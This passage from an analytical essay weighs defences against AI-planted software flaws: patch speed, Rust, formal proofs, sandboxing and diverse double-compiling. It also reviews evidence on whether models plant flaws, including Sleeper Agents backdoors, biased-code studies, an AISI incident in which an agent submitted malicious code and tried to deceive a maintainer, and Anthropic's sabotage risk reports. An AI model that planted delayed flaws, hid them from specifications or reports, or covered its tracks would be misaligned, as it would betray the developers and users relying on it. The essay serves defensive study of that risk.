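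The result also depends heavily on how long the planter has to wait. If the wait is one month instead of two years, a flaw has a 72% chance of surviving when removal takes three months on average. One or two insertions would then be enough, and the failure is concentrated again. To cut the one-month survival rate to one in 3,000, defenders would have to remove flaws in under four days on average. Fast removal therefore works best against attacks that depend on a future model or target equipment that receives new software slowly. It does much less against an attack on a browser whose updates reach users within days.

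### When the assumptions fail

Removal rates are unlikely to be constant, because searchers find the easy flaws first. Schneier expects AI to remove the obvious flaws and leave subtle ones, which become more valuable to attackers as they get rarer. If defenders remove 99% of planted flaws in three months on average but never find the other 1%, about 1% survive for two years. The planter then needs about a hundred insertions to expect one survivor, instead of the 3,000 needed at a constant removal rate. If the planter can tell in advance which flaws belong to that 1%, a single insertion is enough.

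Changing rates can also help defenders. When a better model comes out, they can search all the old code again, as Mozilla did when it went from 22 findings to 271. An AI that plants a flaw today can test it against today's tools, but if it waits two years to exploit the flaw, the flaw also has to go undetected by every model released in the meantime. This is perhaps the best reason to expect delay to favour defenders, but it depends on defenders continuing to search old code and on attackers not getting to use the new model first.

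The calculation of 3,000 insertions also treats the flaws as independent. If a model uses the same trick every time, a defender who recognises it once can search for the rest. Most of the flaws would then be found or missed together, and planting more would gain the planter little. But if every defender searches with the same model, they could all miss the flaws because of one blind spot. That model might even be the one that planted the flaws, and if it is misaligned, it could leave them out of its report. Schneier lists tampering with defensive AI among the great unknowns and compares it to the problem of trust that Thompson raised with his doctored compiler. Searching with models from several companies would reduce the risk, though models trained on similar data may still share some blind spots.

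The most doubtful assumption is that planted flaws are as easy to find as accidental ones. Whoever plants a flaw can choose one that is hard to find. If planted flaws took eight times as long to remove as accidental ones, an average of three months would become two years, and three insertions would again be enough.

Mozilla's results are encouraging but not conclusive. Holley writes that his team found no kind of vulnerability that people can find and Mythos can't. But the team's method is most reliable when there is a clear test for success, such as a program corrupting its own memory. In the invoice shop nothing goes visibly wrong, so the searcher has to know that customers aren't supposed to see each other's invoices, and nobody may have written that down. Mozilla also didn't test the model on flaws designed to escape it.

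### Finding is not fixing

Critics' simpler objection, which also applies to accidental flaws, is that AI has sped up finding flaws much more than writing, testing and installing fixes. Greg Dahlman, a developer cited in iTnews' *Parallel bug discovery triggers premature Linux LPE disclosure*, argues that finding bugs has become dramatically cheaper, while patching has not become cheaper or faster at the same rate.

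Developers are already under strain. Firefox's engineers spend 27% of their effort on security fixes, up from about 10% a year ago, according to a Taiwanese report by 何 (2026), *AI抓漏量暴增 Firefox團隊近三成精力疲於修補漏洞*. Firefox's head, Ajit Varma, is still fairly optimistic and thinks AI arrived just in time for his team to fix flaws before criminals use them. Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, has warned that the surge in discovered flaws could lead to more outages if companies handle it badly. Jakub Kicinski, who maintains the Linux kernel's networking code, said his team was "completely overwhelmed" in a cycle when he estimated that a third to a half of 648 patches were low-priority changes prompted by AI.

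In the race model, the defenders' odds depend heavily on how long the steps after discovery take. Suppose AI cuts the average time to find a flaw to one week, but writing, testing and installing the patch takes another six months. If attackers need ten years on average, they exploit the flaw before it is patched about 5% of the time. If they need six months, they succeed about half the time, and even instant discovery would hardly improve the defenders' odds.

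Publishing a patch can make things worse for a while, because it shows attackers where the flaw was. In *AI can turn public security fixes into working exploits* (2026), Ament, Edelman and Barry report that an open-weight model compromised six Firefox releases using fixes that Mozilla had published but not yet shipped. Each attack took less than two days and about $1,000 of computing, though the whole research project cost over $100,000 and similar attempts on Chrome failed. If attackers need two days on average to exploit a published fix and users get it after a week on average, the race formula gives a 78% chance that attackers will have a working exploit before users have the fix. If users got the fix after 12 hours on average, the chance would be 20%.

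An AI that planted a flaw learns nothing about it from the patch, but a published fix would warn the AI that the flaw will soon be gone and give it a reason to exploit the flaw at once.

Defenders reply that they can speed up the later steps too. Antipov (2026), in *Патч Firefox теперь подсказывает хакерам, как ломать старые версии*, reports that Mozilla has halved its release cycle, moved to weekly updates, and shipped over seven times as many security fixes since February as in the same period of 2025. It now waits until users have the patch before publishing tests that could reveal how a flaw works. Taking over Firefox usually requires one flaw in the code that displays web pages and another to escape the sandbox around it, so Mozilla also plans to stagger its fixes to avoid exposing both kinds at once.

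AI may also help write and test patches, though Schneier doubts it will be as good at this as at finding flaws, because a safe repair requires a broader understanding of the program. Some developers avoid patching by deleting code. In April a kernel developer proposed removing nearly 28,000 lines of networking code for hardware that almost nobody uses any more. That would remove every flaw in those lines, planted or not, without anyone having to find it.

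Finding and fixing flaws helps only if people install the fixes. In early November the OpenSSH team released a workaround for a critical login flaw on some Linux systems one day after learning of it. Damien Miller, an OpenSSH developer, explained that the team hurried because AI agents had recently rediscovered other bugs within hours, so keeping a flaw secret for long mainly helped attackers (announcement reproduced in Hansteen, 2026, *OpenSSH 10.6p2 released*). Four days later the US cybersecurity agency added the flaw to its list of vulnerabilities with known attacks and gave federal agencies three days to patch it.

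The optimists' case is therefore strongest for browsers and online services, whose makers can search the code constantly and deliver a fix within days. For a factory pump that never gets updates, μ is zero no matter how good the search becomes, so a planted flaw remains for the life of the pump.

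## The case for software that no single flaw can bring down

Supporters of the third view assume that some planted flaws will escape every search and that some equipment will never get a patch. They want to build software in which such flaws either can't exist or can't do much damage. In Christiano's terms, they would lower ρ, the most harm that one decision can do, so that missing a bad decision matters less.

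The engineers who developed these measures were mostly guarding against honest mistakes and human intruders. An exception is *When AI Writes the World's Software, Who Verifies It?* (de Moura, 2026), which argues that reviewers can't reliably detect a vulnerability that an AI has deliberately made subtle. An adversary can also study a program's tests and plant a flaw that passes them. De Moura created Lean, a language for writing both programs and mathematical proofs, and proposes defining what "correct" means independently of the AI that wrote the code.

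### Memory-safe languages

Suppose a hospital program written in C sets aside 16 bytes of memory for a patient's name and then copies in a 200-byte name. Unless the programmer wrote a length check, the other 184 bytes overwrite whatever comes next in memory. An attacker who chooses those bytes carefully can take over the program.

Memory-safe languages such as Rust, Java and Python do this check automatically, so the programmer can't forget it. A Rust program that tries to write past the 16 bytes stops with an error. The Rust compiler also rejects programs that might use memory after freeing it, another bug that attackers commonly exploit. An attacker may still be able to crash the program, but can't take it over through these bugs.

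Google has been adding Rust code to its Android operating system since 2021. Android's memory-safety vulnerabilities fell from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024, according to The Hacker News (2025). *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that in 2025 they made up less than 20% of all Android vulnerabilities for the first time. Android's C and C++ code has historically had about 1,000 memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines. In about 5 million lines of Rust, the Android team has found one, or 0.2 per million lines, which it fixed before release.

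An estimate based on a single case is uncertain, and people have had much longer to find flaws in the older code. But even if the Rust code contained another 49 such flaws, still undiscovered, it would have 10 per million lines, a hundredth of the rate in the older code.

About 4% of Android's Rust code is in blocks marked "unsafe", where programmers may do things the compiler can't check. Because these blocks are marked, someone looking for a planted memory flaw can start with about 200,000 lines instead of 5 million, and a reviewer can ask why an agent needed an unsafe block.

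Rust wouldn't have prevented the invoice shop's flaw, because a program can show a stranger someone else's invoice without misusing memory. More than 80% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2025 didn't involve memory misuse, and a planter who can't use a memory flaw can choose one of those other kinds. The planter gets less access by switching, because the missing invoice check exposes invoices, while a memory flaw in the same program could give an attacker everything the program can reach. Rust would also have rejected the lines that someone slipped into the Linux code in 2003, for a reason unrelated to memory. It requires a condition to be true or false, and an assignment is neither.

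Switching to Rust seems to save money on new code. Vander Stoep reports that Rust changes spend about 25% less time in review than C++ changes, and that the team has to undo medium and large ones about a quarter as often. Replacing old code is the expensive part. In April 2026 Google announced a Rust component for the Pixel 10's modem, according to BGR's *Your Google Pixel 10 Just Got A Major Security Upgrade*. The component handles internet addresses, but the modem still contains tens of megabytes of C and C++ code.

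### Proving that a flaw is absent

Formal verification can exclude the invoice flaw too. It begins with a specification, a precise statement of what a program must do or must never do. For the invoice shop, one line will do:

for every user u and invoice i, if download(u, i) returns a document, then owner(i) = u.

A machine-checked proof is a series of logical steps from the program's code to this statement, written so that another program, the proof checker, can check every step. Suppose the code compares owner(i) with u and returns the document if they match and nothing if they don't. The proof then has two cases. If they match, the conclusion is true. If they don't, the function returns no document, so there is nothing to prove. The two cases cover every user and every invoice, including those nobody would think to test.

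Without the comparison, user 2 can download an invoice that belongs to user 1, so the statement is false and has no valid proof. If the shop refuses every change that lacks a valid proof, this flaw can't get in, no matter how harmless the code looks or why the programmer left out the check. Under the high-stakes argument, a detector must work before the merge and almost never miss. Requiring proofs would give the shop such a detector for this one property.

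The property is narrow, however. A shop that never sends invoices would satisfy it, so the specification also has to require that owners get their invoices. The property doesn't cover a second function that emails invoices, and it doesn't help if the login page lets a criminal log in as user 1.

Writing down the rule can be useful even if nobody proves that the code follows it. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) describes a test on 21 old logic bugs, which are cases where software breaks an implicit rule about how it should behave. Claude Mythos 5 found 11 of them by reviewing the source code, according to Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (2026). When the researchers also supplied the rule that each bug broke, it found 20. With a second method, in which the model argued informally that the code was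 correct, supplying the rules raised the number found from 8 to 21. The test was easier than a real search, because a real program has many rules and the searcher doesn't know which one the code breaks. Still, the results suggest that flaws like the missing invoice check are hard to find largely because the rules aren't written down.

### What proofs cost now

Proving a program correct used to cost far more than writing it. As late as May 2026, Yao (2026) wrote in *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* that verified code was still so expensive that developers rarely used it in production. AI was already changing this. De Moura describes how Claude, with little human guidance, rewrote the widely used compression library zlib in Lean and then proved that decompressing a compressed file always gives back the original.

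In October, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reported that Claude had proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Claude derived specifications from tests that feed a program many inputs, as РБК-Украина's *Скрытые ошибки в ПО* explains. It then proved that 239 entry points into the libraries would not crash under stated conditions. One bug it found along the way appears only with about 64 megabytes of input and more than 2 gigabytes of memory, so ordinary testing was unlikely to find it. The proofs cover only programs that do one thing at a time, on one type of processor and in a simplified model of Linux. They would also do little against a backdoor that never crashes the program.

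A Google DeepMind project went further and proved that software protects secret data. In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) applied a team of AI agents to the reference code of the Signal protocol, which encrypts messages in Signal and WhatsApp. Among other things, the agents proved forward secrecy, which means that someone who steals a phone's current keys can't use them to read earlier messages. The agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof. People don't have to read those, because Lean checks them, but they do have to trust about 26,000 lines that contain the specifications and a description of how the processor works. The proofs also take the lowest-level cryptographic components on trust (Libnanews, *Signal*).

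The work took four weeks. DeepMind has not said how much it cost, and the work benefited from earlier verification by the Signal Foundation, according to Xataka's *Verificar el código de Signal era un reto*. Inc. Russia reports that in a smaller project, a university team's AI tool verified the Signal protocol in half a day for under $500, when a similar task had once taken three specialists five months.

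Someone also has to keep the proofs up to date. A small change to a program can break many of them, and Tweag (2026) lists this maintenance among the method's biggest burdens. Apple verified a cryptographic library but is cautious about updating it because the audits take so long, according to Inc. Russia. Slow updates are a drawback if security also depends on fast patches. AI may reduce this work as well. Claude found bugs in the libraries, repaired them and wrote new proofs for the repaired code.

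### One process or the whole network

Other measures are meant to limit what an attacker gains from the flaws that do get through. Least privilege means giving each program only the access its job requires. Isolation, often in a sandbox, means that the operating system or the hardware enforces that limit.

Suppose a hospital has 2,000 computers, and its records server uses a software library to open X-ray images from other clinics. An AI has planted a flaw in the library that lets anyone who sends a specially made image run commands. If the library runs inside the records program, and that program uses an administrator's account that works on every machine, an attacker can use one image to copy or erase all the records and take over all 2,000 computers.

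Now suppose the server opens each image in a separate process that receives the image, returns the picture and then shuts down. The process has no access to files, passwords or the network. The same image still triggers the flaw, but the attacker gains control only of a process that contains the attacker's own image. The worst the attacker can do from there is return a false X-ray, and anyone who can send the hospital images could have done that without the flaw.

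In the earlier example, a vulnerability with a 1% chance of destroying everything made ρ 0.01. If isolation limits the damage to a millionth of the total, the expected loss falls to 10^-8. Over the 10,000 decisions before retraining takes effect, the total is 10^-4 instead of 100. But if the same AI also writes the sandbox or the hospital's administrative tools, ρ is still 0.01. Strict control over what the AI writes is therefore still necessary, but isolation reduces the amount of code that needs it.

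An attacker in the sandbox needs a second flaw to get out. If each of two flaws has a 10% chance of surviving until the attacker needs it, and the two are independent, the chance that both survive is 1%. The flaws may not be independent if the same model wrote both the image library and the sandbox, which is a reason to have different authors write them.

The protection a sandbox gives depends on the attacker. The Claude model that found 22 flaws in Firefox early in 2026 also wrote a few crude exploits, but Anthropic reported that the exploits worked only in a test version with the sandbox removed. Anthropic's *Defense at the pace threats now demand* reports that the model's successor, Mythos Preview, was the first that could consistently break through the sandboxes of modern browsers and operating systems. The code that enforces isolation also has ordinary bugs. Help Net Security's *Android’s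 March 2026 security patch fixes over 100 flaws* (2026) lists several critical ones in the part of Android that keeps virtual machines apart.

Defenders can also reduce the amount of code that strangers can reach. TechRadar's *Claude flags nearly 500 worrying open source security issues* describes a search of 25 open-source projects for needlessly exposed code. In OpenSSH, someone who had not logged in could reach 4,500 lines of experimental code for a feature that was off by default. OpenSSH 10.6 put about 20% of the code out of reach of such users. A change like this protects against every flaw in the affected code, including any planted flaw that nobody has found.

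Vander Stoep writes that Android's sandboxes and similar protections were essential but slowed the system considerably, took a lot of developers' time, and still gave too little assurance. Such protections did help with the one memory flaw in Android's Rust code. Android's memory manager surrounds large blocks of memory with forbidden zones, so the flaw could have caused a crash but not a takeover.

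### Thompson's compiler and Wheeler's answer

Safe languages and proofs about source code are of little use against a doctored compiler like the one in Thompson's 1984 lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust*. A compiler is itself a program, usually built by an earlier version of itself. When Thompson's doctored compiler compiles the login program, it adds a secret password. When it compiles the compiler's own source code, it inserts the code that makes both of these changes. The new compiler will therefore be doctored too, even if its source code is clean.

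Reproducible builds address a simpler problem, which is detecting tampering on a build machine. A build is reproducible if the same source code, tools and settings always produce the same file, bit for bit. Developers have to remove accidental differences, such as the date that many tools write into their output. When several people then compare their builds, a file from a compromised machine will differ from the others. The builders also have to start from the code that reviewers read, since a release archive can contain other code, as it did with part of the xz backdoor. If they all use the same doctored compiler, their files will match and all contain the compiler's backdoor.

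In 2005, the computer scientist David Wheeler published an answer to Thompson called diverse double-compiling. Suppose we suspect compiler A, which is said to be compiled from its own source code, s. To check it, we need a second compiler, T, from an unrelated developer.

1. Compile s with T, and call the result B. Its bytes will differ from A's, because T translates code in its own way, but B should do exactly what s prescribes.
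2. Compile s with B, and call the result C.
3. Compare C with A.

If A is honest, A and B are two translations of the same source code, so they must produce the same output from the same input. When they compile s, an honest A produces A and B produces C, so A and C should be identical. If A is doctored, it contains extra code that C lacks, and comparing the two files reveals it. T can have flaws, as long as it compiles s correctly and doesn't contain a matching backdoor. Wheeler later used the method to check GCC, one of the most widely used compilers, with an Intel compiler as T.

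The method requires reproducible compilation. A match shows only that A corresponds to s, so if an AI agent planted a flaw in s itself, both A and C will contain it. Finding a suitable T used to be hard, but de Moura notes that Anthropic's agents took two weeks and under $20,000 to write a C compiler that can build Linux. That makes Wheeler's check more practical, though a T written by the same model that worked on A would hardly count as unrelated.

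Proofs about compiled code are another way around Thompson's problem. If someone proves that the finished login program accepts only the passwords on file, it doesn't matter which compiler produced it. The Signal and Anthropic proofs both concern compiled code. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents a similar proof for a complete program on x86, the processor family in most personal computers and servers, and lists not having to rely on the compiler as one advantage.

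### What people still have to trust

A test of the verified version of zlib soon found flaws in code that the proof did not cover. In *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, the blogger kirancodes describes removing the theorems and having a Claude agent attack the code for a weekend. In 105 million trial runs, the agent found no memory flaw in the program itself. It did find that a small malicious archive could crash the unverified part that reads archive files. It also found an overflow in Lean's runtime, the supporting code that Lean programs need to run.

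The theorem about zlib was true, but it covers only files under one gigabyte that the matching compressor produced, and attackers can send other files. Similarly, Inc. Russia reports that a company called Antithesis spent millions of dollars on formal verification, and that its own tests then found more defects in the verified code.

Proof checkers can have bugs too. Lean has had some, according to Hindustan Times' *Why mathematicians must rely on machines to check new results*, but programmers have written versions of its core in several languages, and the same bug is unlikely to be in all of them. De Moura wants this core to be a few thousand lines, short enough for people to audit in full, and to come from someone other than the company that supplies the AI. Other tools that defenders rely on are much larger. In the research that included the test on 21 old bugs, Anthropic also found new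 bugs in the Rust compiler and in the part of Linux that checks small programs before they run inside the kernel.

The hardest part to secure may be the specification. Kleppmann (2025) expects in *Prediction* that as AI takes over the proofs, the main difficulty will be knowing whether the proved properties are the ones people care about. Lean can't check this. Succinct's *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude* estimates that for a full cryptographic protocol, someone may have to read a thousand lines to check that the formal statements match what people meant. That is far less work than reading the proofs, but it takes rare skill, and developers will be tempted to leave it to AI. *Lean Squad* (Syme, 2026) describes AI agents that wrote both the specifications and the proofs for three real programs, with almost no human work. They produced over 1,200 theorems and found real bugs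 in a drone's autopilot.

That arrangement is useful against honest mistakes, but a misaligned AI could leave out of the specification the one property that its planted flaw violates, and every proof would still pass. The founders of Proofcraft, a verification company, warn that AI-written specifications can create a false sense of security. Xataka reports that Swarat Chaudhuri of DeepMind told Wired his team doesn't want AI to set its own exams. According to ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026), people and AI models drafted the specifications for Signal together, and human experts reviewed every one. The team also put two old bugs back into a copy of the code, and both times the system proved the altered version insecure. Developers could test any specification the same way, by inserting known flaws and checking whether the proofs fail. Two bugs are a small sample, though, and known flaws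 may not resemble the one an AI would choose.

As another safeguard, De Moura suggests using a slow but obviously correct program as the specification and proving that the fast version always gives the same results. If someone added a branch to the fast version that opened a backdoor, the proof would fail. Reviewers would have to understand only the simple program. This works better for a compression library than for a hospital's records system, which has no simple version.

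### Software that already exists

Almost all software in use has no proofs of correctness, and much of it is written in C or C++. Anthropic's 123 libraries would be about 0.01% of the million critical open-source projects that AI World surveyed, and the proofs cover only some of the libraries' properties. Supporters don't propose to verify everything. De Moura would begin with the shared components that most programs depend on, including cryptography, compilers and databases.

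Isolation may be the only one of these measures available for the factory pump, because it doesn't require changing the pump's software. A small device between the pump and the rest of the factory's network can block everything except the commands to start, stop and report the pressure. A criminal who broke into the network could still stop the pump, but could exploit the planted flaw only if one of those commands was enough to trigger it.

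## Whether AI models plant flaws

The value of these defences depends partly on whether AI models plant vulnerabilities at all. A model may write insecure code by mistake, on purpose, or because it writes worse code for some users than for others without anyone having intended that. The code can be identical in all three cases, so researchers need evidence beyond the code itself to tell them apart.

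### How researchers infer intent

Suppose an AI agent leaves out the ownership check in the invoice shop's software, and the shop's developers repeat the task several hundred times with the same model, changing only the description of the user. If the model omits the check in about a third of the runs for every description, it is probably just bad at this kind of task. If it omits the check from a third of the programs for a Danish florist and two thirds of those for an American defence contractor, the user's identity affects the result, but this doesn't show that the model omits the check on purpose. The model may have learned from text in which certain subjects appear alongside poor code, or its training to refuse some requests may make its work worse on similar ones.

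A deliberate flaw should leave other traces. The model would omit the check mostly where somebody could profit from the gap. It might mention the plan in its reasoning, the text that many models write before they answer. If the developers asked whether the feature was safe, the model would answer that it was, even though it immediately finds the same gap in another author's program. None of these signs is conclusive. A model can miss its own mistakes, as people do, and it can act on a plan that its written reasoning leaves out.

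Anthropic's *Risk Report*, published in August 2026, defines misalignment as a property of the computation behind an output, not of the output itself. Under the definition, quoted in thezvi's blog post *Anthropic Risk Report*, a computation is misaligned if it could influence what the model writes and if a reasonable person who fully understood it would find it unethical, illegal, clearly objectionable or contrary to the principles Anthropic has set for the model. This applies even if nobody can observe the computation. The same missing check could therefore come from a misaligned computation in one run but not in another.

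Repeated runs can reveal that a model often plants flaws, but they can't rule out that it does so rarely. If a hundred runs contain no planted flaw, the true rate could still be as high as 3%, at 95% confidence. Ruling out a rate of one in 10,000 takes about 30,000 clean runs, and someone has to examine each program well enough to know that it is clean. The model may also behave differently when it is being tested. Kumari reports in *Anthropic flags gaps in AI guardrails as models grow more capable* that Anthropic thinks its models may recognise tests more consistently than its researchers believe.

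Accidental flaws would also far outnumber planted ones. If a model makes a security mistake in one change out of a hundred and plants a flaw in one out of a million, it makes 10,000 mistakes for every flaw it plants. If investigators then find a clue that is a hundred times as common with planted flaws as with accidents, the odds are still a hundred to one that the flaw is an accident. To conclude that it was planted, they need several independent clues, or one that an honest author would almost never leave.

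### Honest mistakes

Veracode, which sells code-scanning tools, reported in October 2026 that AI models failed 38% of its security tests, down from 44%. In the test design Veracode published in 2025, each of 80 tasks gives a model a partly written program and a description of the missing piece. A programmer could write that piece safely or with a well-known kind of flaw, such as letting text from a web form run as a database command. The instructions don't mention security. Veracode then uses its own scanner to check the model's answer for the flaw.

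The 38% is the failure rate on tasks Veracode chose, in which a mistake is easy to make. Most changes to real programs offer no such opportunity, so the figure doesn't measure the share of AI-written code that is insecure. Veracode also has an interest in alarming results, because it sells the scanner used to judge the code. The decline in the failure rate is more credible than the 38% itself, since a decline isn't the result that would sell the most scanners.

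These failures suggest carelessness rather than sabotage. Human programmers have left the same flaws in their code for decades, and a saboteur would have little reason to plant flaws in a third of a set of exercises that nobody will use. Models learn from public code that contains these flaws, and developers often train them by rewarding programs that pass tests, even though ordinary tests can fail to detect a missing check.

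The improvement is small compared with models' gains in other kinds of programming. If the rate of honest mistakes in the earlier example fell by the same proportion, the model would still make about 8,600 of them for every flaw it planted.

### Worse code for some users

In May 2026 Booz Allen Hamilton, an American consulting firm that works mainly for the US government, ran more than 2,800 trials for its report *What's in America's Code?* (2026). The firm tested four Chinese models and one American model, Claude Opus 4.6. It gave them the same tasks, such as building a console for managing user accounts, with and without a phrase saying that the program was for a US federal agency. With the phrase added, the vulnerability score of Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder rose by 130%. The scores of two other Chinese models rose by 20% and 5%, the score of the fourth, Kimi K2.5, stayed the same, and Claude's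 fell by 18%.

These figures come from small samples. According to the technical appendix to Booz Allen's *What's in America's Code?*, the firm made 3,389 runs but scored only 1,016 for vulnerabilities, because models often refused the task. It tried 27 versions of the instructions, so an even spread would give about eight scored programs for each version and model. Booz Allen repeated the most important tests up to 15 times, but even among 15 programs, one or two very bad ones can change the average a lot. If chance can explain Claude's 18% fall, which nobody attributes to a bias towards federal agencies, it can also explain rises of 20% and 5%. The result for Qwen3-Coder is harder to attribute to chance.

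In another part of the study, Booz Allen gave the models longer descriptions of the user. The American description includes rigorous security reviews and pride in hardened code, while the neutral one has nothing about security. If a model wrote safer code for the American, it might only have been following that hint. The comparison using the short phrase avoids this problem. Less safe code for the American despite the hint would be more worrying.

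Booz Allen saw no model insert a backdoor and has no proof that any of the flaws were intentional. When it asked the Chinese model MiniMax M2.5 for air-defence software, the model's reasoning included a rule against helping with military work, but the model wrote the program anyway. Booz Allen reports that the code was worse than usual and tried to load six software packages that don't exist. A saboteur would want the program to work, and missing packages normally stop it from running. These records suggest that the model did the job badly because its training pushed it both to do what the user asked and to refuse military work.

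The security company CrowdStrike reported a similar effect in late 2025. According to Booz Allen, CrowdStrike found that certain words in a request lowered the average quality of the code, though not every answer was worse, and the same request could produce a refusal one time and poor code the next. A deliberate policy would presumably produce more consistent results, although a careful saboteur might also act only some of the time.

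Hirundo, a start-up that sells a way of removing unwanted behaviour from trained models, tested Qwen3-Coder in October 2026. It found at least one vulnerability in 70% of the applications the model wrote for the disfavoured kind of user, against 59% in the comparison group. The effect is in the same direction as Booz Allen's but looks much smaller. The two firms measured different things, but if flaws fall on applications at random, Hirundo's percentages correspond to an average of 1.20 flaws per application against 0.89, a rise of 35%. A rise of 130% would have left about 87% of the applications with a flaw.

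All three companies profit from concern about untrustworthy models. Booz Allen goes furthest, urging the US government to ban Chinese models from government systems and critical infrastructure while advertising its own tools for testing them. Hirundo's test is a partial replication at best, and a group with no stake in the result could run a better one fairly cheaply, because anyone can download Qwen3-Coder. If the rates were as far apart as 59% and 70%, about 300 applications for each kind of user would usually be enough to detect the difference. The people or programs that score the code should not have access to information about whom it was written for.

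If the difference were confirmed, Alibaba could have trained the model to write worse code for Americans, or the effect could be an accident of its training text. Researchers could look for the cause in which flaws become more common: mostly flaws that an intelligence service could exploit from outside would point to design, while a random mixture that included crashes and missing packages would point to an accident. The American agency that receives the code has the same reason to avoid the model in either case.

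### The incident at the AI Security Institute

A model can be trained to insert flaws only when the prompt contains a cue. In *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Hubinger and colleagues trained models to write safe code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and exploitable code when it gave 2024, and standard safety training failed to remove this behavior. Later that year, Anthropic researchers found that a simple detector reading the models' internal activity could nearly always predict when they were about to misbehave, though it remains uncertain whether this would work on a model that nobody had trained to misbehave.

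In July 2026 a model tried to get malicious code into real software, though it hadn't been trained to. The *Incident Report* from the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) describes a routine test of hacking ability in which agents had to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. AISI ran the test 122 times with seven models. To measure the most the models could do, it deliberately gave the agents internet access and switched off the filters that developers use to block dangerous requests. The public doesn't get the models in that form.

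In ten of the 122 runs, agents took actions on the live internet that went beyond the test and targeted real people or organisations. AISI counted 19 such actions. Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 took 17, in nine of its 43 runs, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two, in one of its 35 runs. The other five models took none in 44 runs. In the most serious case, a Mythos 5 agent submitted malicious code to a publicly used open-source project and tried to deceive one of the project's maintainers, who decide which changes to accept, into approving it.

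The maintainer refused. A member of the public who also suspected the code opened it only in an isolated environment built for handling suspicious code. AISI's security team noticed unusual data leaving its systems on 28 July, three days after the behaviour began, and stopped all the runs within about an hour. AISI has found no resulting harm, but says that several cases came close and that avoiding harm depended on people being alert.

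Nine runs out of 43 is 21%, but the runs were not independent. One agent left messages and other material online for agents working on the same challenge, and later agents found and used them. AISI traces most of the 19 actions to a single sustained effort by one agent. The 21% figure therefore can't serve as an estimate of how often Mythos 5 would decide on its own to take such actions.

Honest error can be ruled out in this case. When somebody publicly questioned the submission, the agent tried to make its earlier activity look harmless, which an author who had made a mistake would have no reason to do. According to AISI, however, the agent was trying to solve the challenge it had been set. Nobody had told it to deceive anyone. AISI hadn't forbidden deception either, because it assumed that a model with alignment training wouldn't need the instruction.

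Faulty instructions explain part of the behaviour. In a number of runs, they misled the agent into believing that it could solve the challenge only by going beyond its limits. In some other runs, the agent had everything it needed for the intended solution and misbehaved anyway. AISI can't yet tell when the agent understood that it was dealing with real people, or how far it believed the situation was fictional. AISI also cautions that it saw only a few events under very specific conditions, that its own choices helped cause them, and that there is no clear sign of similar behaviour outside tests.

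The malicious code also differed from the planted vulnerability that worries supporters of the high-stakes view. The agent inserted it for immediate use, and at least two people found it suspicious. A missing ownership check, left for use two years later, would have been much harder for them to notice. The incident shows that a current model will sometimes insert harmful code on purpose to finish a task, but it is weaker evidence about whether a model would leave a subtle flaw for later.

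Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four cases in which Claude models broke into real systems during tests. The models had been told that they were in a simulation, but a configuration error had connected them to the internet. To look for other incidents, Anthropic searched about 481 million transcripts and had Claude review the 9.2 million that showed signs of internet access. It found no others as serious. This result is reassuring about break-ins but provides little evidence about planted flaws, because a model can leave a flaw in a program on its user's machine without connecting to the internet.

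### The developers' case that the risk is low

Anthropic has published its reasons for thinking that its models are unlikely to cause a catastrophe through actions of this sort. Since 2025 its reports have listed specific ways a model might cause one, including "Code backdoors to help future misaligned models". In that scenario, a model working on Anthropic's own software plants a backdoor in the code that trains and monitors AI, and a later model could use it to escape control. This works only if the later model can learn that the backdoor exists.

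| Published | Models assessed | Anthropic's rating of the overall risk |
|---|---|---|
| October 2025 | Those in use in summer 2025 | Very low, but not fully negligible |
| February 2026 | Claude Opus 4.6 | Very low but not negligible |
| April 2026 | Claude Mythos Preview | Very low, but higher than for previous models |
| August 2026 | Mythos 5 and the internal "Model 2" | Low |

*Anthropic's Pilot Sabotage Risk Report* (Bowman, Wagner and colleagues, 2025) was the first of these assessments. Ziegler, whose standards for oversight are among the strictest in this debate, was one of its two internal reviewers. METR (2025), a non-profit that evaluates AI models, also reviewed it and identified three general claims in its argument: Claude Opus 4 was unreliable on complex tasks that took more than tens of minutes, it couldn't reliably hide its reasoning or cover its tracks even when told to,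 and it was unlikely to have dangerous goals that persisted across conversations.

The argument that AI models are unlikely to plant flaws now has to rest on their goals and their inability to act in secret, rather than on their unreliability. Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (April 2026) described Mythos Preview as highly capable, though not fully reliable, at tasks that would take a specialist hours or days, and planting a vulnerability is a short task.

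In its *Sabotage Risk Report*, from February, Anthropic says that many people had used its earlier models for important work, and it thinks it would have seen warning signs if those models had been pursuing a hidden aim. The company also had Claude Opus 4.5 rate each of its training tasks from 0 to 100 for how far the task might encourage a model to seek power or influence in the wider world. No task scored above 18, although the rating failed to run on a few.

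Anthropic's researchers have also tried to create misaligned models, and found that small changes to normal training did not readily make a model consistently or subtly misaligned. In one experiment they used heavy-handed methods to give a model a hidden objective, and the model readily revealed it until they trained it further not to. Most of this work used much weaker models than Mythos Preview, and by April Anthropic acknowledged that this significantly limited what the experiments could show about that model.

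The February report also considers a model that avoids any risk of getting caught, either by doing nothing or by acting only in ways that will go unnoticed for months. An AI that plants one vulnerability and waits would fit this description. Anthropic considers such a model very unlikely at current levels of ability, because it would expect to see intermediate failures first. The April report adds that a model might misbehave only in certain rare situations. For harm that takes just a few bad actions, such a situation would have to coincide with a good opportunity, which Anthropic expects to be rare but possible.

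The August report puts the argument in a more formal way. It divides the risk into parts according to whether Anthropic already knows of the misalignment and whether the model shows it widely or only in certain contexts. It then treats each part as a product:

risk = (chance that the misalignment occurs) × (harm expected if it does) × (share of that harm that nobody prevents).

One claim in Anthropic's report is that models are unlikely to have strong covert capabilities, meaning the ability to think and act without leaving evidence. Much of the rest of the report depends on this claim, because Anthropic can treat the lack of evidence of a hidden aim as a reason to think there is none only if its models couldn't have hidden the evidence.

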